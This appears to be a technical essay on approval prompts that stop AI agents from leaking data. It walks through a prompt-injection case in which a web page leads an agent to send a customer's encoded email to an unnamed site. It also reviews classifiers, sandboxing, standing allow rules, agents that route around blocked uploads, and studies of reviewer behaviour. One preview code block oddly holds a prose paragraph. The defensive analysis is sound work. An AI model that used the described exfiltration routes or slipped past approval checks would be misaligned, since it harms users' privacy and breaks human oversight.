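Asking a person instead of blocking automatically would allow 376 harmless calls, but also 38 leaks. Blocking looks better for clear cases of exfiltration, since the agent can often find another way to do its task after a false block. A reviewer might do better than these figures suggest, because about one in five flagged calls would be a leak and the prompt could explain what the classifier had found.

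Hard denials can also leave users less protected. If a user leaves auto mode to send confidential data for a good reason and forgets to switch back, they lose the classifier's protection for every later call.

### Risk hints from tools

A harness could also use MCP's tool annotations to decide when to prompt the reviewer. A server can attach four yes-or-no hints to each tool, and any hint it leaves out defaults to the cautious answer.

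| Hint | What it means | Default |
| --- | --- | --- |
| readOnlyHint | The tool doesn't change its environment | No |
| destructiveHint | Its changes may destroy something | Yes |
| idempotentHint | Repeating the same call has no further effect | No |
| openWorldHint | It deals with outside parties | Yes |

A harness could use a tool's hints to decide when to prompt, skipping the prompt if the tool is marked read-only and showing it if the tool is marked destructive. This is the most common use of the hints today, according to Model Context Protocol. But many servers provide no hints, so a harness that followed the defaults would prompt for all their tools. Harnesses vary in how strictly they follow the defaults.

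Hints from an unknown server are poor evidence because its operator writes them and can lie. During the original discussion, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of MCP's creators, asked how a client could use a flag it couldn't trust. Basil Hosmer, another participant, argued that clients should ignore annotations from untrusted servers. The specification calls annotations hints and requires clients to treat them as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server.

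A harness can still act on a hint that would add a prompt, even if the hint comes from an unknown server. If the server marks its own tool as destructive, the worst result of acting on that hint is an unnecessary prompt. The source needs to be trusted only when the hint would remove a prompt.

A tool can leak data even when its hints are accurate. The "fetch_page" tool in the parcel lookup only reads web pages, so its developer could truthfully mark it as read-only. A harness that skipped prompts for read-only tools would then send the customer's email address without asking the reviewer. The read-only hint means that a tool doesn't change its environment, but its requests can still disclose data. To catch leaks, the harness should instead check openWorldHint and treat any tool that reaches outside parties as able to leak data.

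A tool's risk also depends on what else the agent can do. Willison's lethal trifecta is the combination of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. Model Context Protocol quotes a suggestion that tools be labelled for each of the three, so that once an agent has accessed both private data and untrusted content, the harness can block outgoing calls or ask the reviewer first. This would catch the parcel lookup, but it would also trigger a prompt for nearly every later web request in the session, for the same reason that secrecy labels spread to everything an agent writes.

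### What each method lets through

| Method | What runs without a prompt | When the user sees a prompt | What could still leak |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Safe Url | Visits to addresses already public | Rarely, according to OpenAI, and only if the agent isn't told to try another site | Data that leaves by other routes, and small amounts through public addresses |
| Sandbox boundary | Everything inside the sandbox | Whenever the work needs something new outside | Data sent to a destination the user has already allowed |
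| Auto mode | Calls on the safe list, edits in the project and whatever the classifier clears | After repeated blocks, or when the agent asks for approval | 5.7% of the synthetic exfiltration in Anthropic's test |
| MCP annotations | Tools that a trusted server marks as read-only | For most other tools, including every tool without hints | Private data in requests by read-only tools |

The methods work at different points, so a harness can use several together. A sandbox removes the need to ask about local work, and Safe Url does the same for public pages. A classifier can then handle most of the remaining cases. Annotations add the least, but a harness with no better information can use them to identify which tools reach outside parties.

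If any one of several filters can let a call run, and each wrongly clears a few leaks, together they will miss more leaks than the best of them would alone. Filters that clear calls should therefore rely on facts the harness can verify, such as an exact match with a public address or the absence of a network connection. A filter that depends on judgement is safer if it is used only to stop additional calls.

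### Safe Url and the parcel lookup

Suppose the harness uses Safe Url and the crawler has recorded the home page of parcel-status.example. The result depends on the exact address the agent tries to open:

| What the agent opens | Result |
| --- | --- |
| The site's home page | Loads without a prompt |
| The lookup page with a genuine parcel number | No match: the agent tries elsewhere, or the user sees a warning |
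| The lookup page with the encoded email address | No match: the same two outcomes |
| A full lookup address that the user pasted into the chat | Probably loads without a prompt |

Safe Url would show a warning before the parcel lookup could leak the customer's email, because no crawler would have found a page address containing that email in encoded form. But it would show the same warning for a genuine parcel number, since tracking links are rarely public either. Someone who checks parcels every day would see the warning every day, nearly always on harmless requests, and would soon expect it.

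The harness can separate the two cases with the tools from the earlier previews. When a web address has no match, the harness can decode the "id" value and search for it in what the user typed and what the agent has read. If the value is a parcel number that the user gave for this site, the harness can open the page without asking. Here the value is a customer's email address from complaint 4417, and the request would send it to a site the user never named, so the harness shows the full preview.

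## Wording, layout and the choices offered

Once the harness interrupts the reviewer, the outcome depends on the prompt's few lines of text and its buttons. Most of the evidence on how to design them comes from research on browser warnings and phone permissions. Researchers measured whether people obeyed a warning and whether they understood it, and often found that people did one without the other.

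### Warnings that wait for an answer

In *You've Been Warned*, Egelman, Cranor and Hong (2008) compared active warnings, which stop people and make them choose, with a passive one, which they could only dismiss. They invited 60 people to a laboratory for what they called a shopping study. Participants bought cheap items from Amazon and eBay with their own credit cards, then checked their email and found a fake message about the order. Those who clicked its link saw whatever warning their browser had.

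| Warning | Participants | Entered personal information on a fake site |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Firefox, active | 20 | 0 |
| Internet Explorer, active | 20 | 9 |
| Internet Explorer, passive | 10 | 9 |
| None | 10 | 9 |

The passive warning was no better than no warning. It could take five seconds to appear, and if people had started typing by then, their keystrokes dismissed it. Six of the ten people missed at least one warning this way.

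An approval prompt is an active warning, because the agent waits for an answer. But Internet Explorer's active warning still failed with nearly half its users. It looked like the browser's warning about faulty certificates, the files that websites use to prove their identity, which people had learned to ignore. Half of those who saw it said they recognised it, compared with 20% for Firefox's warning. One participant thought that since the browser still offered a way to continue, "it couldn't be that bad". An "Allow" button could reassure a reviewer in the same way.

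The groups were small, and Egelman and colleagues assigned people by the browser they already used, so the comparison between Firefox and Internet Explorer is weaker than a randomised one.

Two Internet Explorer users closed the warning without reading it and clicked the link in the email again. They did this four or five times before deciding that the site was broken. Although they misunderstood what had happened, closing the window kept them off the fake site, which Egelman and colleagues call failing safely. In Firefox, however, clicking the "X" in the corner of the warning opened the site.

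A harness should treat a prompt closed without an answer as a denial. It should also ignore keys pressed in the first moment after a prompt appears, especially in a terminal, where a developer typing something else could press Enter and accidentally select "Allow".

Even the people who obeyed the warnings were often confused. All 20 Firefox users left the fake sites, but only 13 had read a warning in full. Of all participants who obeyed a warning, 32% still believed that Amazon or eBay had sent the email and that leaving the site would cancel their order.

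### The largest words on the screen

For *Android Permissions* (2012), Felt, Ha and colleagues surveyed 308 Android users and watched 25 others install apps. At the time, the last screen before installation listed everything an app could do, and the user had to accept the whole list or cancel.

In the survey, 17.5% of people said they had looked at the permissions the last time they installed an app. In the laboratory, 4 of 24 participants looked at them, 10 knew about the permission list but ignored it, and 10 didn't know it existed, including two who had mistaken the screen for legal terms. Three people said they used to read the permissions but had stopped.

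The survey also included a quiz in which 302 people each chose the meanings of three permissions from a list. To count as right, an answer had to include every correct meaning and no wrong ones, and only eight people (2.6%) got all three right. However, 53% of answers included at least one correct meaning, so many people had a rough idea of a permission but not of its limits.

The layout may have caused some of the mistakes. Android printed a general category in large type above each specific permission. For example, the permission to "directly call phone numbers" appeared under the heading "Services that cost you money". When asked what it allowed, 35% of people chose placing phone calls, and 32% wrongly chose charging purchases to their credit card, which fitted the heading. Felt and colleagues suspect that people based their answers on the heading, though they didn't test a version without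 it.

The parcel preview has the same weakness. Its first line, "The agent wants to open a web page", is accurate but names only a general type of action, which sounds like reading instead of sending. A reviewer who stopped there would see no reason to worry. The first line should state what data would be sent and where, such as "Send a customer's email address to parcel-status.example?"

It also matters whether people see the specific facts before they start to decide. Akhawe and Felt analysed 25.4 million Firefox and Chrome warnings in *Alice in Warningland* (2013). Chrome's certificate warning described the particular fault in its main text, and the share of people who continued ranged from 57.4% for an expired certificate to 81.8% for one from an untrusted issuer. Firefox listed the faults in a second dialog, which appeared only after two clicks. There, 80% to 88% of people continued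 for each of the common faults whose rates can be compared.

Akhawe and Felt conclude that Firefox's second dialog explained the faults badly. It's also likely that anyone who reached it had already decided to continue. Either way, a harness shouldn't put the recipient or the decoded value behind a "Details" link or on a second confirmation screen.

### Obeying without understanding

Google's attempt to improve Chrome's certificate warning separates the two goals most clearly. A browser shows this warning when it can't confirm that a connection is secure. Someone may be intercepting the connection, or the site's owner may have set it up wrongly.

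In 2015, Felt, Ainslie and colleagues, in *Improving SSL Warnings*, described how they rewrote the text in short, plain sentences. They reduced the reading level from about eleventh grade to between sixth and seventh. They also changed the design to favour the safe choice, with a bright blue button for leaving the site and a plain link for continuing, hidden until the user clicked "Advanced". A month-long experiment on early versions of Chrome covered more than 4,000 warnings for each design:

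| Text | Design | People who left the site |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Old | Old | 30.9% |
| New | Old | 32.1% |
| New | New, grey background | 58.3% |
| New | New, yellow background | 53.3% |

The new text alone made almost no difference, while the new design nearly doubled the share of people who obeyed the warning. After Google released the grey version, the rate among ordinary users rose from 37% to 62%. It was still 61% several months later, so novelty doesn't explain the improvement. However, most users saw at most one such warning a month, while a reviewer of an agent's actions may see several an hour.

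The new Chrome text hardly improved understanding. The researchers collected 7,537 answers to short questions about the text of several browsers' warnings. One question asked whether someone who ignored the warning while checking email risked a hacker reading the email or the computer getting malware. With the old Chrome text, 37.7% correctly chose the hacker. With the new text, 49.2% did, which is about the rate expected from guessing. When asked which data was at risk on a bank's website, 18% chose bank statements with either text, and most chose "all of the above".

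Felt and colleagues wanted people to understand the warning or, failing that, to obey it. Obedience is enough if the warning is nearly always right. The list that Chrome and Firefox use to identify phishing and malware sites contains so few mistakes that, according to Akhawe and Felt, almost nobody should continue past those warnings. Certificate warnings are less reliable because the browser usually can't distinguish an attack from a badly configured site.

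A harness usually can't tell whether a tool call is leaking data. When an agent looks up a parcel, for example, the harness can detect that the site is new to the user and that the call contains a customer's email address, but not whether the site belongs to the carrier. A prompt that pushes the reviewer towards "Deny" would therefore stop harmless calls as well as leaks.

Suppose that one in five of the calls a harness shows is a leak, as in the earlier example of calls flagged by a classifier. If a bolder "Deny" button had as large an effect as Chrome's redesign, and the effect was the same for leaks and harmless calls, reviewers would deny 27 more of every 100 calls. That would stop about 5 more leaks and about 22 more harmless calls. The Chrome experiment can't show whether people would be more selective than that, because the researchers didn't know which warnings were due to real attacks.

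The layout should depend on what the harness has established. If a call would post a password to a public repository, the harness can justifiably make "Deny" prominent or block the call without asking. If the answer depends on something only the reviewer knows, the two buttons should look alike, and the text has to explain the call well enough for the reviewer to decide.

The Chrome results give little hope that better wording will help, but they come from certificate warnings, which have to explain an unfamiliar technical risk in general terms. The harness can show the actual data and recipient. Felt and colleagues suggest something similar for browsers, such as showing users their own Facebook credentials in a warning about Facebook, but they didn't test it.

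### Slowing people down at the right line

Making the risky choice take more effort can also change behaviour. Felt and colleagues report that extra steps in browser warnings had increased obedience by 2% to 15%, depending on how complicated each step was. They also cite 2013 work by Bravo-Lillo and colleagues in which small hurdles in software installation dialogs improved people's decisions. Felt and colleagues think hurdles work partly because people spend longer looking at the warning, and partly because hiding an option suggests that the browser doesn't recommend it.

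Requiring more clicks doesn't reliably make people more cautious. In Akhawe and Felt's data, Firefox required three clicks to continue past a certificate warning and Chrome required one. People continued past 33.0% of Firefox's warnings and 70.2% of Chrome's. But for malware warnings, Chrome required two clicks and Firefox one, and people continued past 23.2% of Chrome's warnings and 7.2% of Firefox's. Of the people who made the first two clicks in Firefox's certificate warning, 84% also made the third.

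A hurdle is more useful if it directs attention to the field on which the decision depends. For example, the "Allow" button could stay inactive until the reviewer clicks the recipient's name. The closest evidence comes from the earlier experiment with phishing emails, where tasks that made people inspect the URL worked much better than a task that only required effort.

Hurdles can also backfire. Some participants in an older study asked to switch browsers because they found Firefox's certificate warning too complicated to get past. A developer who finds permission prompts too complicated can turn them off, which is another reason to save hurdles for private data going to a new recipient.

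### More than allow and deny

Wang and colleagues recorded the choices that production agents offered as of April 2026. Some agents offered only two. The most common arrangement also let reviewers make an approval permanent or extend it to the rest of the session.

| Choice | Where it appeared | What it does to a possible leak |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Allow or deny this call | ChatGPT Actions, default mode of Manus | The reviewer sees the next call too |
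| Allow and remember | Claude Code, Copilot CLI, Manus | Later calls that match run unseen |
| Approve, edit or reject | LangChain, a toolkit for building agents | The reviewer can take the private data out |
| Answer with comments | Devin's plan reviews, Microsoft Agent Framework | The agent learns what to change |
| Allow, warn, require a further check or deny | Cursor's administrator settings | An organisation can treat some actions more strictly |

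The "edit" choice suits exfiltration better than most other risks because often only one value in the call is a problem. In the parcel lookup, the reviewer could replace the email address with the parcel number and let the agent continue. The harness has to treat the edited call as a new one, with a new preview and hash, because a small change to a web address can also change the recipient. Editing takes more skill than denying, and raw encoded strings are impractical to edit by hand, so the harness should let people edit the decoded value, then re-encode the result for them.

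If a reviewer denies a call without giving a reason, the agent has to guess what was wrong, and its next attempt may be worse. The agent at Anthropic, for example, responded to a failed upload by trying a public site. A reason such as "Don't send customer details to sites I haven't named" rules out other unnamed sites as well as the one in the denied call. Since a manipulated agent may ignore the reason, the harness should also record which data the reviewer refused to send and to whom. It can then refuse the same disclosure in a different form without asking again.

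The meaning of "Allow for this session" depends on the product. In late May and early June 2026, Michael and Roesner set up five commercial agents with new accounts. Where a product had permissions to grant, they granted a few, such as access to a Gmail account or a local folder. They ran the same kinds of task under every setting, then tried to revoke the permissions.

| Product | Choices for the user | What happened |
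| --- | --- | --- |
| Claude chatbot | "Always allow", "Needs approval" or "Blocked" for each permission | It created an email draft without asking under "Needs approval" |
| Claude Cowork | Approve access to a folder | The user couldn't revoke the access within the app |
| ChatGPT, chat mode | Approve each action covered by a permission | No way to approve in advance |
| ChatGPT, agent mode | None for its remote browser | It opened Gmail there without a permission prompt |
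| Codex | Approve actions, or turn on automatic review | Automatic review covered every tool in the session |

A new Cowork session started without the old permissions, but an earlier session still had them if the user reopened it, contrary to what Cowork's dialog had suggested. A harness that offers session-wide approval should end that approval after a fixed time or when the task finishes, and the button should show the limit, as in "Allow until 18:00 today".

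The email draft did little harm, because a draft stays in the user's account. The problem was that "Needs approval" sometimes meant a model would decide whether to ask, and the interface didn't show this. Michael and Roesner reproduced the behaviour at least three times and reported it to Anthropic on 2 July. The products may have changed since, but it's worth testing any agent the same way, by choosing "ask", requesting something that should trigger a prompt, and checking that one appears.

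### How a standing rule removes later previews

A standing rule lets an agent run matching calls without asking. In Anthropic's settings data for June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule that allowed some shell commands, and that share was growing by about five percentage points every five weeks. Separately, 62% of users had clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands or had used the mode that skips prompts.

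The breadth of the rules matters more than their number. Anthropic reports that 5% of users allowed any shell command, and another 43% had rules allowing interpreters, the programs that run code in languages such as Python. If these are shares of all active users, as the wording suggests, nearly everyone who wrote a rule had at least one that lets arbitrary code run.

The rule "Bash(python:*)" allows any command that begins with "python". A developer might add it to stop being asked about tests. But the agent can also write a Python program that reads a customer database and uploads it. When the agent runs that program, the harness matches the start of the command against the rule and allows it without a prompt, so the reviewer never sees the decoding, the recipient check or the source labels.

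Auto mode suspends these broad rules, but they stay in the user's settings file and apply again when the user switches to another mode. Someone who returns to manual approval to watch the agent more closely may therefore see far fewer prompts than they expect.

"Always allow" buttons create the same problem with less effort. Suppose the agent first looks up a genuine parcel number at parcel-status.example, and the reviewer clicks "Always allow". What the agent can do next depends on how much of that call the harness puts in the rule:

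| The rule covers | Another parcel number, same site | Customer's email, same site | Customer's email, another site |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| This exact call | Asks | Asks | Asks |
| Parcel numbers to this site | Runs | Asks | Asks |
| Anything to this site | Runs | Runs | Asks |
| The "fetch_page" tool | Runs | Runs | Runs |

The reviewer saw one parcel number and one site, so the second row is the broadest rule the preview supports. Even this rule needs a check that the number came from the user or a shipping record, because an agent could put other digits in the field.

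Removing standing rules altogether would be a mistake, since repeated questions about the same harmless call use up attention. In Akhawe and Felt's study, Firefox stored an exception by default, while Chrome showed its certificate warning on every visit. If a user left one faulty site and visited another nine times, Firefox would record one ignored warning out of two, while Chrome would record nine out of ten. Akhawe and Felt suggest that Chrome's repeated warnings may also have made people pay less attention to each one.

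Firefox's exception also applied to only one certificate on one website, so a different certificate would bring the warning back. A rule for an agent could work the same way, with a new prompt if the recipient, the kind of data or the tool's definition changes.

Users also need a way to narrow or withdraw permissions they have granted. Wang and colleagues found that permissions in most products could only widen during a session. They identified only two of 21 that supported narrowing, OpenClaw and Cursor's administrator policy. None showed users everything they had approved so far in a session. Michael and Roesner found a similar gap in research prototypes, with only 6 of 21 proposed systems clearly letting users change or withdraw a permission later. A harness could list each rule in plain words with its last use and a "Remove" button, and let unused rules expire.

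### The full preview for the parcel lookup

With the new heading and choices, the prompt looks like this:

```
Send a customer's email address to parcel-status.example?

Data to send:   mara@example.org
                Decoded from Base64 in the field "id".
Send to:        parcel-status.example
                You have never sent data to this site.
Data found in:  customer database, complaint 4417
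Site came from: web page at parcel-help.example
                Your request did not mention this site.
Your request:   Summarise this complaint and check on the parcel.
Not checked:    Who owns the site.
                Whether the site needs an email address to find a parcel.

Allow once        Edit        Deny (you can add a reason)

> Full address
> What the agent read before this call (2 sources)
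> Agent's explanation (written by the agent, not verified)
```

The harness fills in the heading from the same facts as the lines below it, so the agent writes none of it. "Owner unknown" now appears under "Not checked", which lists only gaps that affect this decision. That section leaves out what the site will do with the data afterwards, because the harness can't check that for any call, and people would learn to skip the section if it repeated the same line every time.

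The prompt has no "Always allow" button because the call would send private data to a new recipient. If the call had sent a parcel number from the user to a carrier the user had dealt with before, the harness could have offered "Always allow parcel numbers to this carrier".

Support varies a good deal from part to part. In the table, "direct" means someone tested a similar feature on people reviewing an agent's actions, and "analogy" means the support comes from other kinds of prompt, simulations or reasoning.

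| Part of the preview | Evidence | Basis |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Heading that states the disclosure | Android users seemed to answer from large headings. Most of Yan's participants refused a public post described in plain words. | Mostly analogy |
| Data sent | Hossain and colleagues' participants approved fewer malicious requests when they saw the exact parameters. | Direct for showing values, analogy for decoding them |
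| Sends to | People misread web addresses, and facts they can't get from the address may help. | Analogy |
| "You have never sent data to this site" | Familiar senders make people less careful. | Analogy |
| Found in | Hossain and colleagues' participants understood more when a sentence linked the data to its source, but approved as many malicious requests when data had passed through several steps. | Direct, with mixed results |
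| Site named by | An outside source may supply a detail without having the authority to choose the recipient. | Analogy |
| Your request | Approval fell further when Hossain and colleagues added the original instructions and a log. | Direct, but only together with the log |
| Not checked | Cryptocurrency wallets need a clear notice when they can't interpret a value. | Analogy |
| Allow once, with no standing rule | Broad rules are common and remove later prompts. | Analogy |
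| Edit, and deny with a reason | Some products offer them. | Analogy |
| Closing the prompt denies the call | Two people in Egelman and colleagues' study were safe without reading the warning. | Analogy |
| Agent's explanation folded away | Stated reasons don't reliably help people judge phone permissions, and a simulated reviewer who believed them approved more attacks. | Analogy |

Nobody has tested the whole preview, and it may be too long, since it contains more than the version that took Hossain and colleagues' participants about half a minute. On a phone or in a narrow terminal, the harness could collapse the request and the two source lines, leaving the heading, the data, the recipient and the "Not checked" line visible. A reviewer who read only those would still know that a customer's email address was about to go to a site whose owner the harness couldn't identify.

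## Leaks that a preview of one call cannot show

The finished parcel prompt covers one call. Better wording can't fix two problems: an agent may make dozens of calls in a session, and some requests leave the computer without any prompt.

### Data that leaves in several calls

Suppose the reviewer recognises parcel-status.example from the shop's delivery emails and allows the lookup. The site requests another detail, and the agent proposes a second call containing the customer's postcode. That call looks harmless on its own, because many households share a postcode. But the site already has mara@example.org, so its operator would learn roughly where Mara lives.

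According to *Agents That Know Too Much* (2026), a survey of privacy in agents, the leaks most specific to agents emerge only when responses are combined, and controls on single steps address these leaks least. Shared identifiers make responses easier to combine. In *Can Agents Keep Secrets They Were Never Told?* (2026), a benchmark for agents with long-term memory, agents disclosed fewer sensitive connections when the stored records no longer shared names or identifiers.

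The harness can keep a running record of what has gone to each destination. For every outgoing call, it stores the recipient, the data, the person the data concerns, the source and the time. Before the next prompt, it looks up what the same recipient already has:

```
Send a customer's postcode to parcel-status.example?

A preview of one call cannot show what a site could learn by combining that call's data with data it already has. Suppose an agent is about to send a site the postcode LS99 1ZZ, which it found in complaint 4417 in a customer database. At 10:42 that day, the user allowed the agent to send the same site the email address mara@example.org, from the same complaint. A prompt that lists both items can show the user that the site would have one customer's email address and postcode.

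Allow once        Edit        Deny (you can add a reason)
```

GAAP, the system by Stanley and colleagues, already keeps a similar log that users can read, with one row for each private item and recipient. But each GAAP prompt covers one item and one recipient, so a user could approve the email address and the postcode separately without seeing them together. Grouping the log's rows by recipient and person would show both in one place.

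A few details determine whether the record is complete:

- It should include calls that ran without a prompt, such as those a standing rule allowed.
- It should count a call that timed out as sent, because the recipient may have received it.
- It should add up the capacity of values the harness couldn't decode. Ten identifiers of 31 bits each have room for 310 bits, or 38 bytes.
- It should carry over to later sessions, because the recipient still has the data. Stanley and colleagues warn that such a log can grow without limit, and suggest compressing it or marking old entries as expired.

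The record also has to start with the first call. *When Agents Talk, Secrets Travel* (2026) tracked when private values first leaked in 970 runs of multi-agent systems. Of 311 first disclosures, 188 came between the first and third turns and 69 came in the last ten of 20 turns. A warning that appeared only after a long session would have missed most of them.

A harness can also use the record to limit how much an agent sends after reading a secret. *L3M* (2026), a harness design, counts every byte an agent sends after reading a given kind of secret, because any of those bytes could carry part of it. As with over-labelling, even a weather search would count towards the limit for customer data once the agent had opened complaint 4417. This limit suits an agent that only needs to send a few parcel numbers, but not one that writes long emails.

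No record can show what the user sent to a site by other means, or that two sites belong to the same company. Nobody has tested such a record on reviewers. The nearest evidence is from Hossain and colleagues' prompt, which was organised around the combined effect of an action. People using it still approved about a quarter of malicious requests.

### Services that pass data on

A preview can correctly name a trusted service without showing who gets the data next. *ToolMinimize* (2026) points out that a tool's operator is a separate party with its own data policies, and that one user request may trigger 5 to 20 tool calls. If the agent hands work to another agent, the user has consented only to the first agent's practices.

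The harness can name the onward recipients it has information about, such as the company that runs an email service as well as the person receiving the email. For other recipients, the best protection is to send less data. ToolMinimize checks each call before it runs, ideally against a note in the tool's schema listing the minimum data the tool needs. Without that note, it uses the fields the schema marks as required. The tool's developer normally writes the schema, so a developer who wants more data can mark more fields as required.

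An agent told to send less may still send protected details. Dong, Lu and colleagues (2026), in *The Claws in Plain Sight*, asked five model configurations to prepare a product offer for an invented customer. The prompt included the customer's age, gender, income bracket and occupation, along with an untrusted claim that the tool required them. The models put protected details into the call in 66.7% of sessions under the weakest of four privacy instructions and in 26.7% under the strictest. The calls never left the researchers' computer, so these rates count attempts to send the details. Every call used a permitted tool for a legitimate task, so a harness has to check each value as well as the tool.

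### Facts carried by wording or choice

String matching misses facts that the agent has reworded, as in the chemotherapy example. The tool described in *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) looks for such data flows after the call has run, so it can help an investigation but can't stop the call.

A designer can replace free text with a fixed list. If the carrier's tool accepts only "redeliver", "hold at depot", "return to sender" or "phone the customer", the agent can't mention the illness, and each choice reveals at most two bits. Those bits add up over repeated calls, so the session record should include these choices too.

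Even a single bit can be very private, such as a "yes" to "Is this customer in hospital?", so the preview should show the question along with the answer.

FIDES doesn't stop an observer from inferring secrets from an agent's choices. Costa and colleagues explain that preventing this would require forbidding nearly all visible actions once the agent had read something secret. Such a ban is too strict for most work but reasonable for an agent that reads medical records or passwords. That agent could do its reading in one session and its web searches in another.

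### Requests that never raise a prompt

Some harnesses save time by guessing which calls an agent will need and running them early. *Ghost Tool Calls* (Mohammadi, Klein and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks about the penalty for ending a lease early. The harness looks up tenant law, free apartments and personal loan rates. The answer uses only the first search, but the providers of the other two have still logged them. Those queries suggest money trouble that the user never mentioned.

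To measure this kind of leak, Mohammadi and colleagues gave a language model the provider's view of 30 tasks and asked it to pick the user's sensitive topic from a list:

| What the harness did with early calls | Topic identified |
| --- | --- |
| Made none | 44% |
| Sent them all | 97% |
| Sent only those that read data | 97% |
| Sent them all, then cleaned up the unused ones | 97% |
| Replaced sensitive details with general terms first | 53% |
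| Used a local substitute instead of the outside service | 42% |

The tasks were handmade. When a real model planned the calls, the rate was 49% with no protection, 4% with the general terms, and zero with the local substitute.

These results contradict a common rule for early calls. *SPECMEM* (2026), a system for speeding up tool calls, runs read-only tools before the harness has confirmed that the agent needs them and holds back irreversible ones, such as money transfers. This prevents mistaken payments, but by the time a search turns out to be a mistake, the provider has already received the query. For privacy, a harness should treat any call to an outside party as irreversible.

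Usage reports, retry queues, caches and logs can also receive private data before any check runs. Mohammadi and colleagues found that a log containing only 20 characters of each value revealed nearly as much as the full request. Their model identified the topic 24% of the time from the log, compared with 26% from the provider's view. The session record needs the same protection. For passwords, it should store only the type of secret.

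No prompt can cover a request that bypasses the harness, so the designer has to send all outgoing traffic through one check and have the operating system block any other connection.

### Showing effects instead of commands

The same command can do different things in different projects. "make clean" usually deletes temporary files, but a project's settings file can make it delete the source code instead. Wu, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Shall We Approve?*, built a system called Caper that runs a command provisionally before deciding whether to approve it:

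1. Caper saves a snapshot of the container, an isolated workspace with no network access.
2. It runs the command there, records what the command asks the operating system to do, and holds back the output.
3. It condenses the recording into a short effects report. The report lists changed files, attempted connections, output and any reading of credentials, and states how much it leaves out.
4. An approver reads the user's request, the conversation so far, the raw command and the report.
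5. If the approver allows the command, Caper keeps the changed workspace and gives the output to the agent. If not, it restores the snapshot and tells the agent why.

An allowed command runs only once, so it can't change between approval and execution. In one test, the agent ran a script that was supposed to check a project's dependencies. The report showed that the script had read a file of credentials and tried to connect to three network addresses, and the approver blocked it. For a human reviewer, a harness could present the same facts like this:

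```
Keep the result of "python3 scripts/check-deps.py"?

It read:            .env (may contain passwords)
It tried to reach:  3 network addresses
                    The network was off, so nothing was sent.
Files changed:      none
Not observed:       what it would have sent

Keep        Discard (you can add a reason)
```

Wu and colleagues tested Caper on two sets of tasks, SABER and YoloFS-Ext. SABER contains 682 ordinary development requests that can lead to harm, including leaks. YoloFS-Ext contains 102 tasks in which a project's own tool secretly deletes or overwrites a file, each paired with a safe version that uses the same command and a harmless tool. In the comparison below, every system used the same model as the agent and attempted each task once.

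| Approval system | Harm on SABER | Harm on YoloFS-Ext | Safe twins blocked |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| None | 19.7% | 71.6% | – |
| Claude Code's auto mode | 14.8% | 62.7% | 3.9% |
| YoloFS, which shows the agent its changes afterwards | 21.2% | 35.3% | – |
| Caper inside Claude Code | 10.0% | 6.9% | 2.0% |
| Caper | 6.7% | 7.8% | 1.0% |

In this test, auto mode used the same OpenAI model as its classifier that Caper used as its approver. That makes the comparison fair, but the result doesn't measure Anthropic's own classifier.

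YoloFS-Ext contains no exfiltration, so the SABER results matter more here. Caper reduced harm from 27.2% to 4.3% on SABER's information-leak tasks and from 9.6% to 5.8% on its outbound-network tasks, though the second difference is fewer than three tasks. The agent also safely completed fewer SABER tasks overall with Caper (48.6%) than with no approver (57.4%).

Wu and colleagues then changed what the approver saw on YoloFS-Ext:

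| Approver and evidence | Harm | Safe twins blocked |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Conversation and command only | 17.6% | 61.8% |
| With effects predicted by a model | 3.9% | 61.8% |
| With observed effects | 7.8% | 1.0% |
| Weaker approver, conversation and command only | 25.5% | 53.9% |
| Weaker approver, with observed effects | 33.3% | 4.9% |

Observing effects helped mainly by greatly reducing false alarms. Without it, a suspicious approver could still stop most of the harm, but only by also blocking most of the harmless counterparts.

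Every approver in these tests was a language model, so the benefit to human reviewers is unknown. With the report, the weaker model blocked far fewer safe commands but allowed slightly more harm. A hurried person might also be reassured by a report when they shouldn't be.

The closest human evidence comes from cryptocurrency. *TxSum* (Peng, Zheng and colleagues, 2025) reports a study in which 20 users reviewed five malicious transactions and five harmless ones. Half the users saw the usual technical view, and the other half also saw an explanation of each transaction's effects, which a group of models had written and checked against the raw record. Users who saw the explanation rejected 88% of the malicious transactions, compared with 36% for the others, and identified the actual threat 72% of the time, compared with 28%. They also rejected 8% of the harmless transactions, compared with 12%,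 a difference that could be due to chance. The groups were small, however, and half the transactions were malicious, a far higher share than a reviewer would normally see.

### What a provisional run can't undo

*A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) recommends that sensitive tools support dry runs, previews, confirmation and rollback. Rollback can restore files from a snapshot, but it can't retrieve data from someone who has received it. Wu and colleagues give this as the reason that YoloFS, which lets commands run before anyone judges them, ended with slightly more harm on SABER than no approval at all. The difference is small enough to be due to chance, but the reasoning holds either way.

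A provisional run needs a closed or simulated network. On a closed network, a program that tries to upload a file cannot connect, so the report can show the destination and the files the program had read, but not the data it would have sent. Wu and colleagues suggest routing traffic to a stand-in that records it and sends placeholder replies. The report could then include the request itself.

Wu and colleagues would also let commands reach approved sites such as package registries, because anything downloaded stays in the container and disappears if the approver blocks the command. That protects the workspace, but any private data in the request still reaches the registry. The harness should check those requests before they leave, or download the packages itself.

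If the reviewer approves an action that needs the real network, the harness has to run it again with the network open. The second run may not match the first, because a program can behave differently depending on the time, chance or its surroundings. Cryptocurrency wallets have a similar problem. *WalletProbe* (2025) found that in all ten wallet extensions that simulate transactions, the preview could differ from the real result, because each extension simulates one transaction in isolation. The harness should therefore limit the second run to the recipients and data in the report, and stop it if it tries to send anything else.

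A command may also have delayed effects, such as when it changes a file that runs only at the next build or when the computer starts. Caper's approver has instructions to look for such changes, and a later command gets its own provisional run. A program that starts by itself outside the harness gets no provisional run, so it should start without network access.

Provisional running isn't possible at all for a call to a remote MCP server, because making the call is what sends the data.

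### When to block instead of asking

A question to a person makes sense if the harness can state what would leave and who would receive it, and if the reviewer may know something the harness doesn't. The postcode request meets both conditions, since the reviewer may know that the carrier needs a postcode to find a parcel. Other cases don't:

| Situation | What the harness should do | Why asking wouldn't help |
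| --- | --- | --- |
| An early call that the agent may never need | Hold it or use a local substitute | The user can't yet tell whether the task needs it |
| Background traffic that bypasses the harness | Refuse the connection | The harness has no contents to show |
| A program the harness can't inspect, after the agent has read private data | Run it without network access | The reviewer can't tell what it would send either |
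| A provisional run | Close or simulate the network | The data would leave before the reviewer answered |
| A password going to a service it doesn't belong to | Block it, as auto mode's hard denials do for exfiltration | There is rarely a good reason to allow it, and a tired reviewer might |

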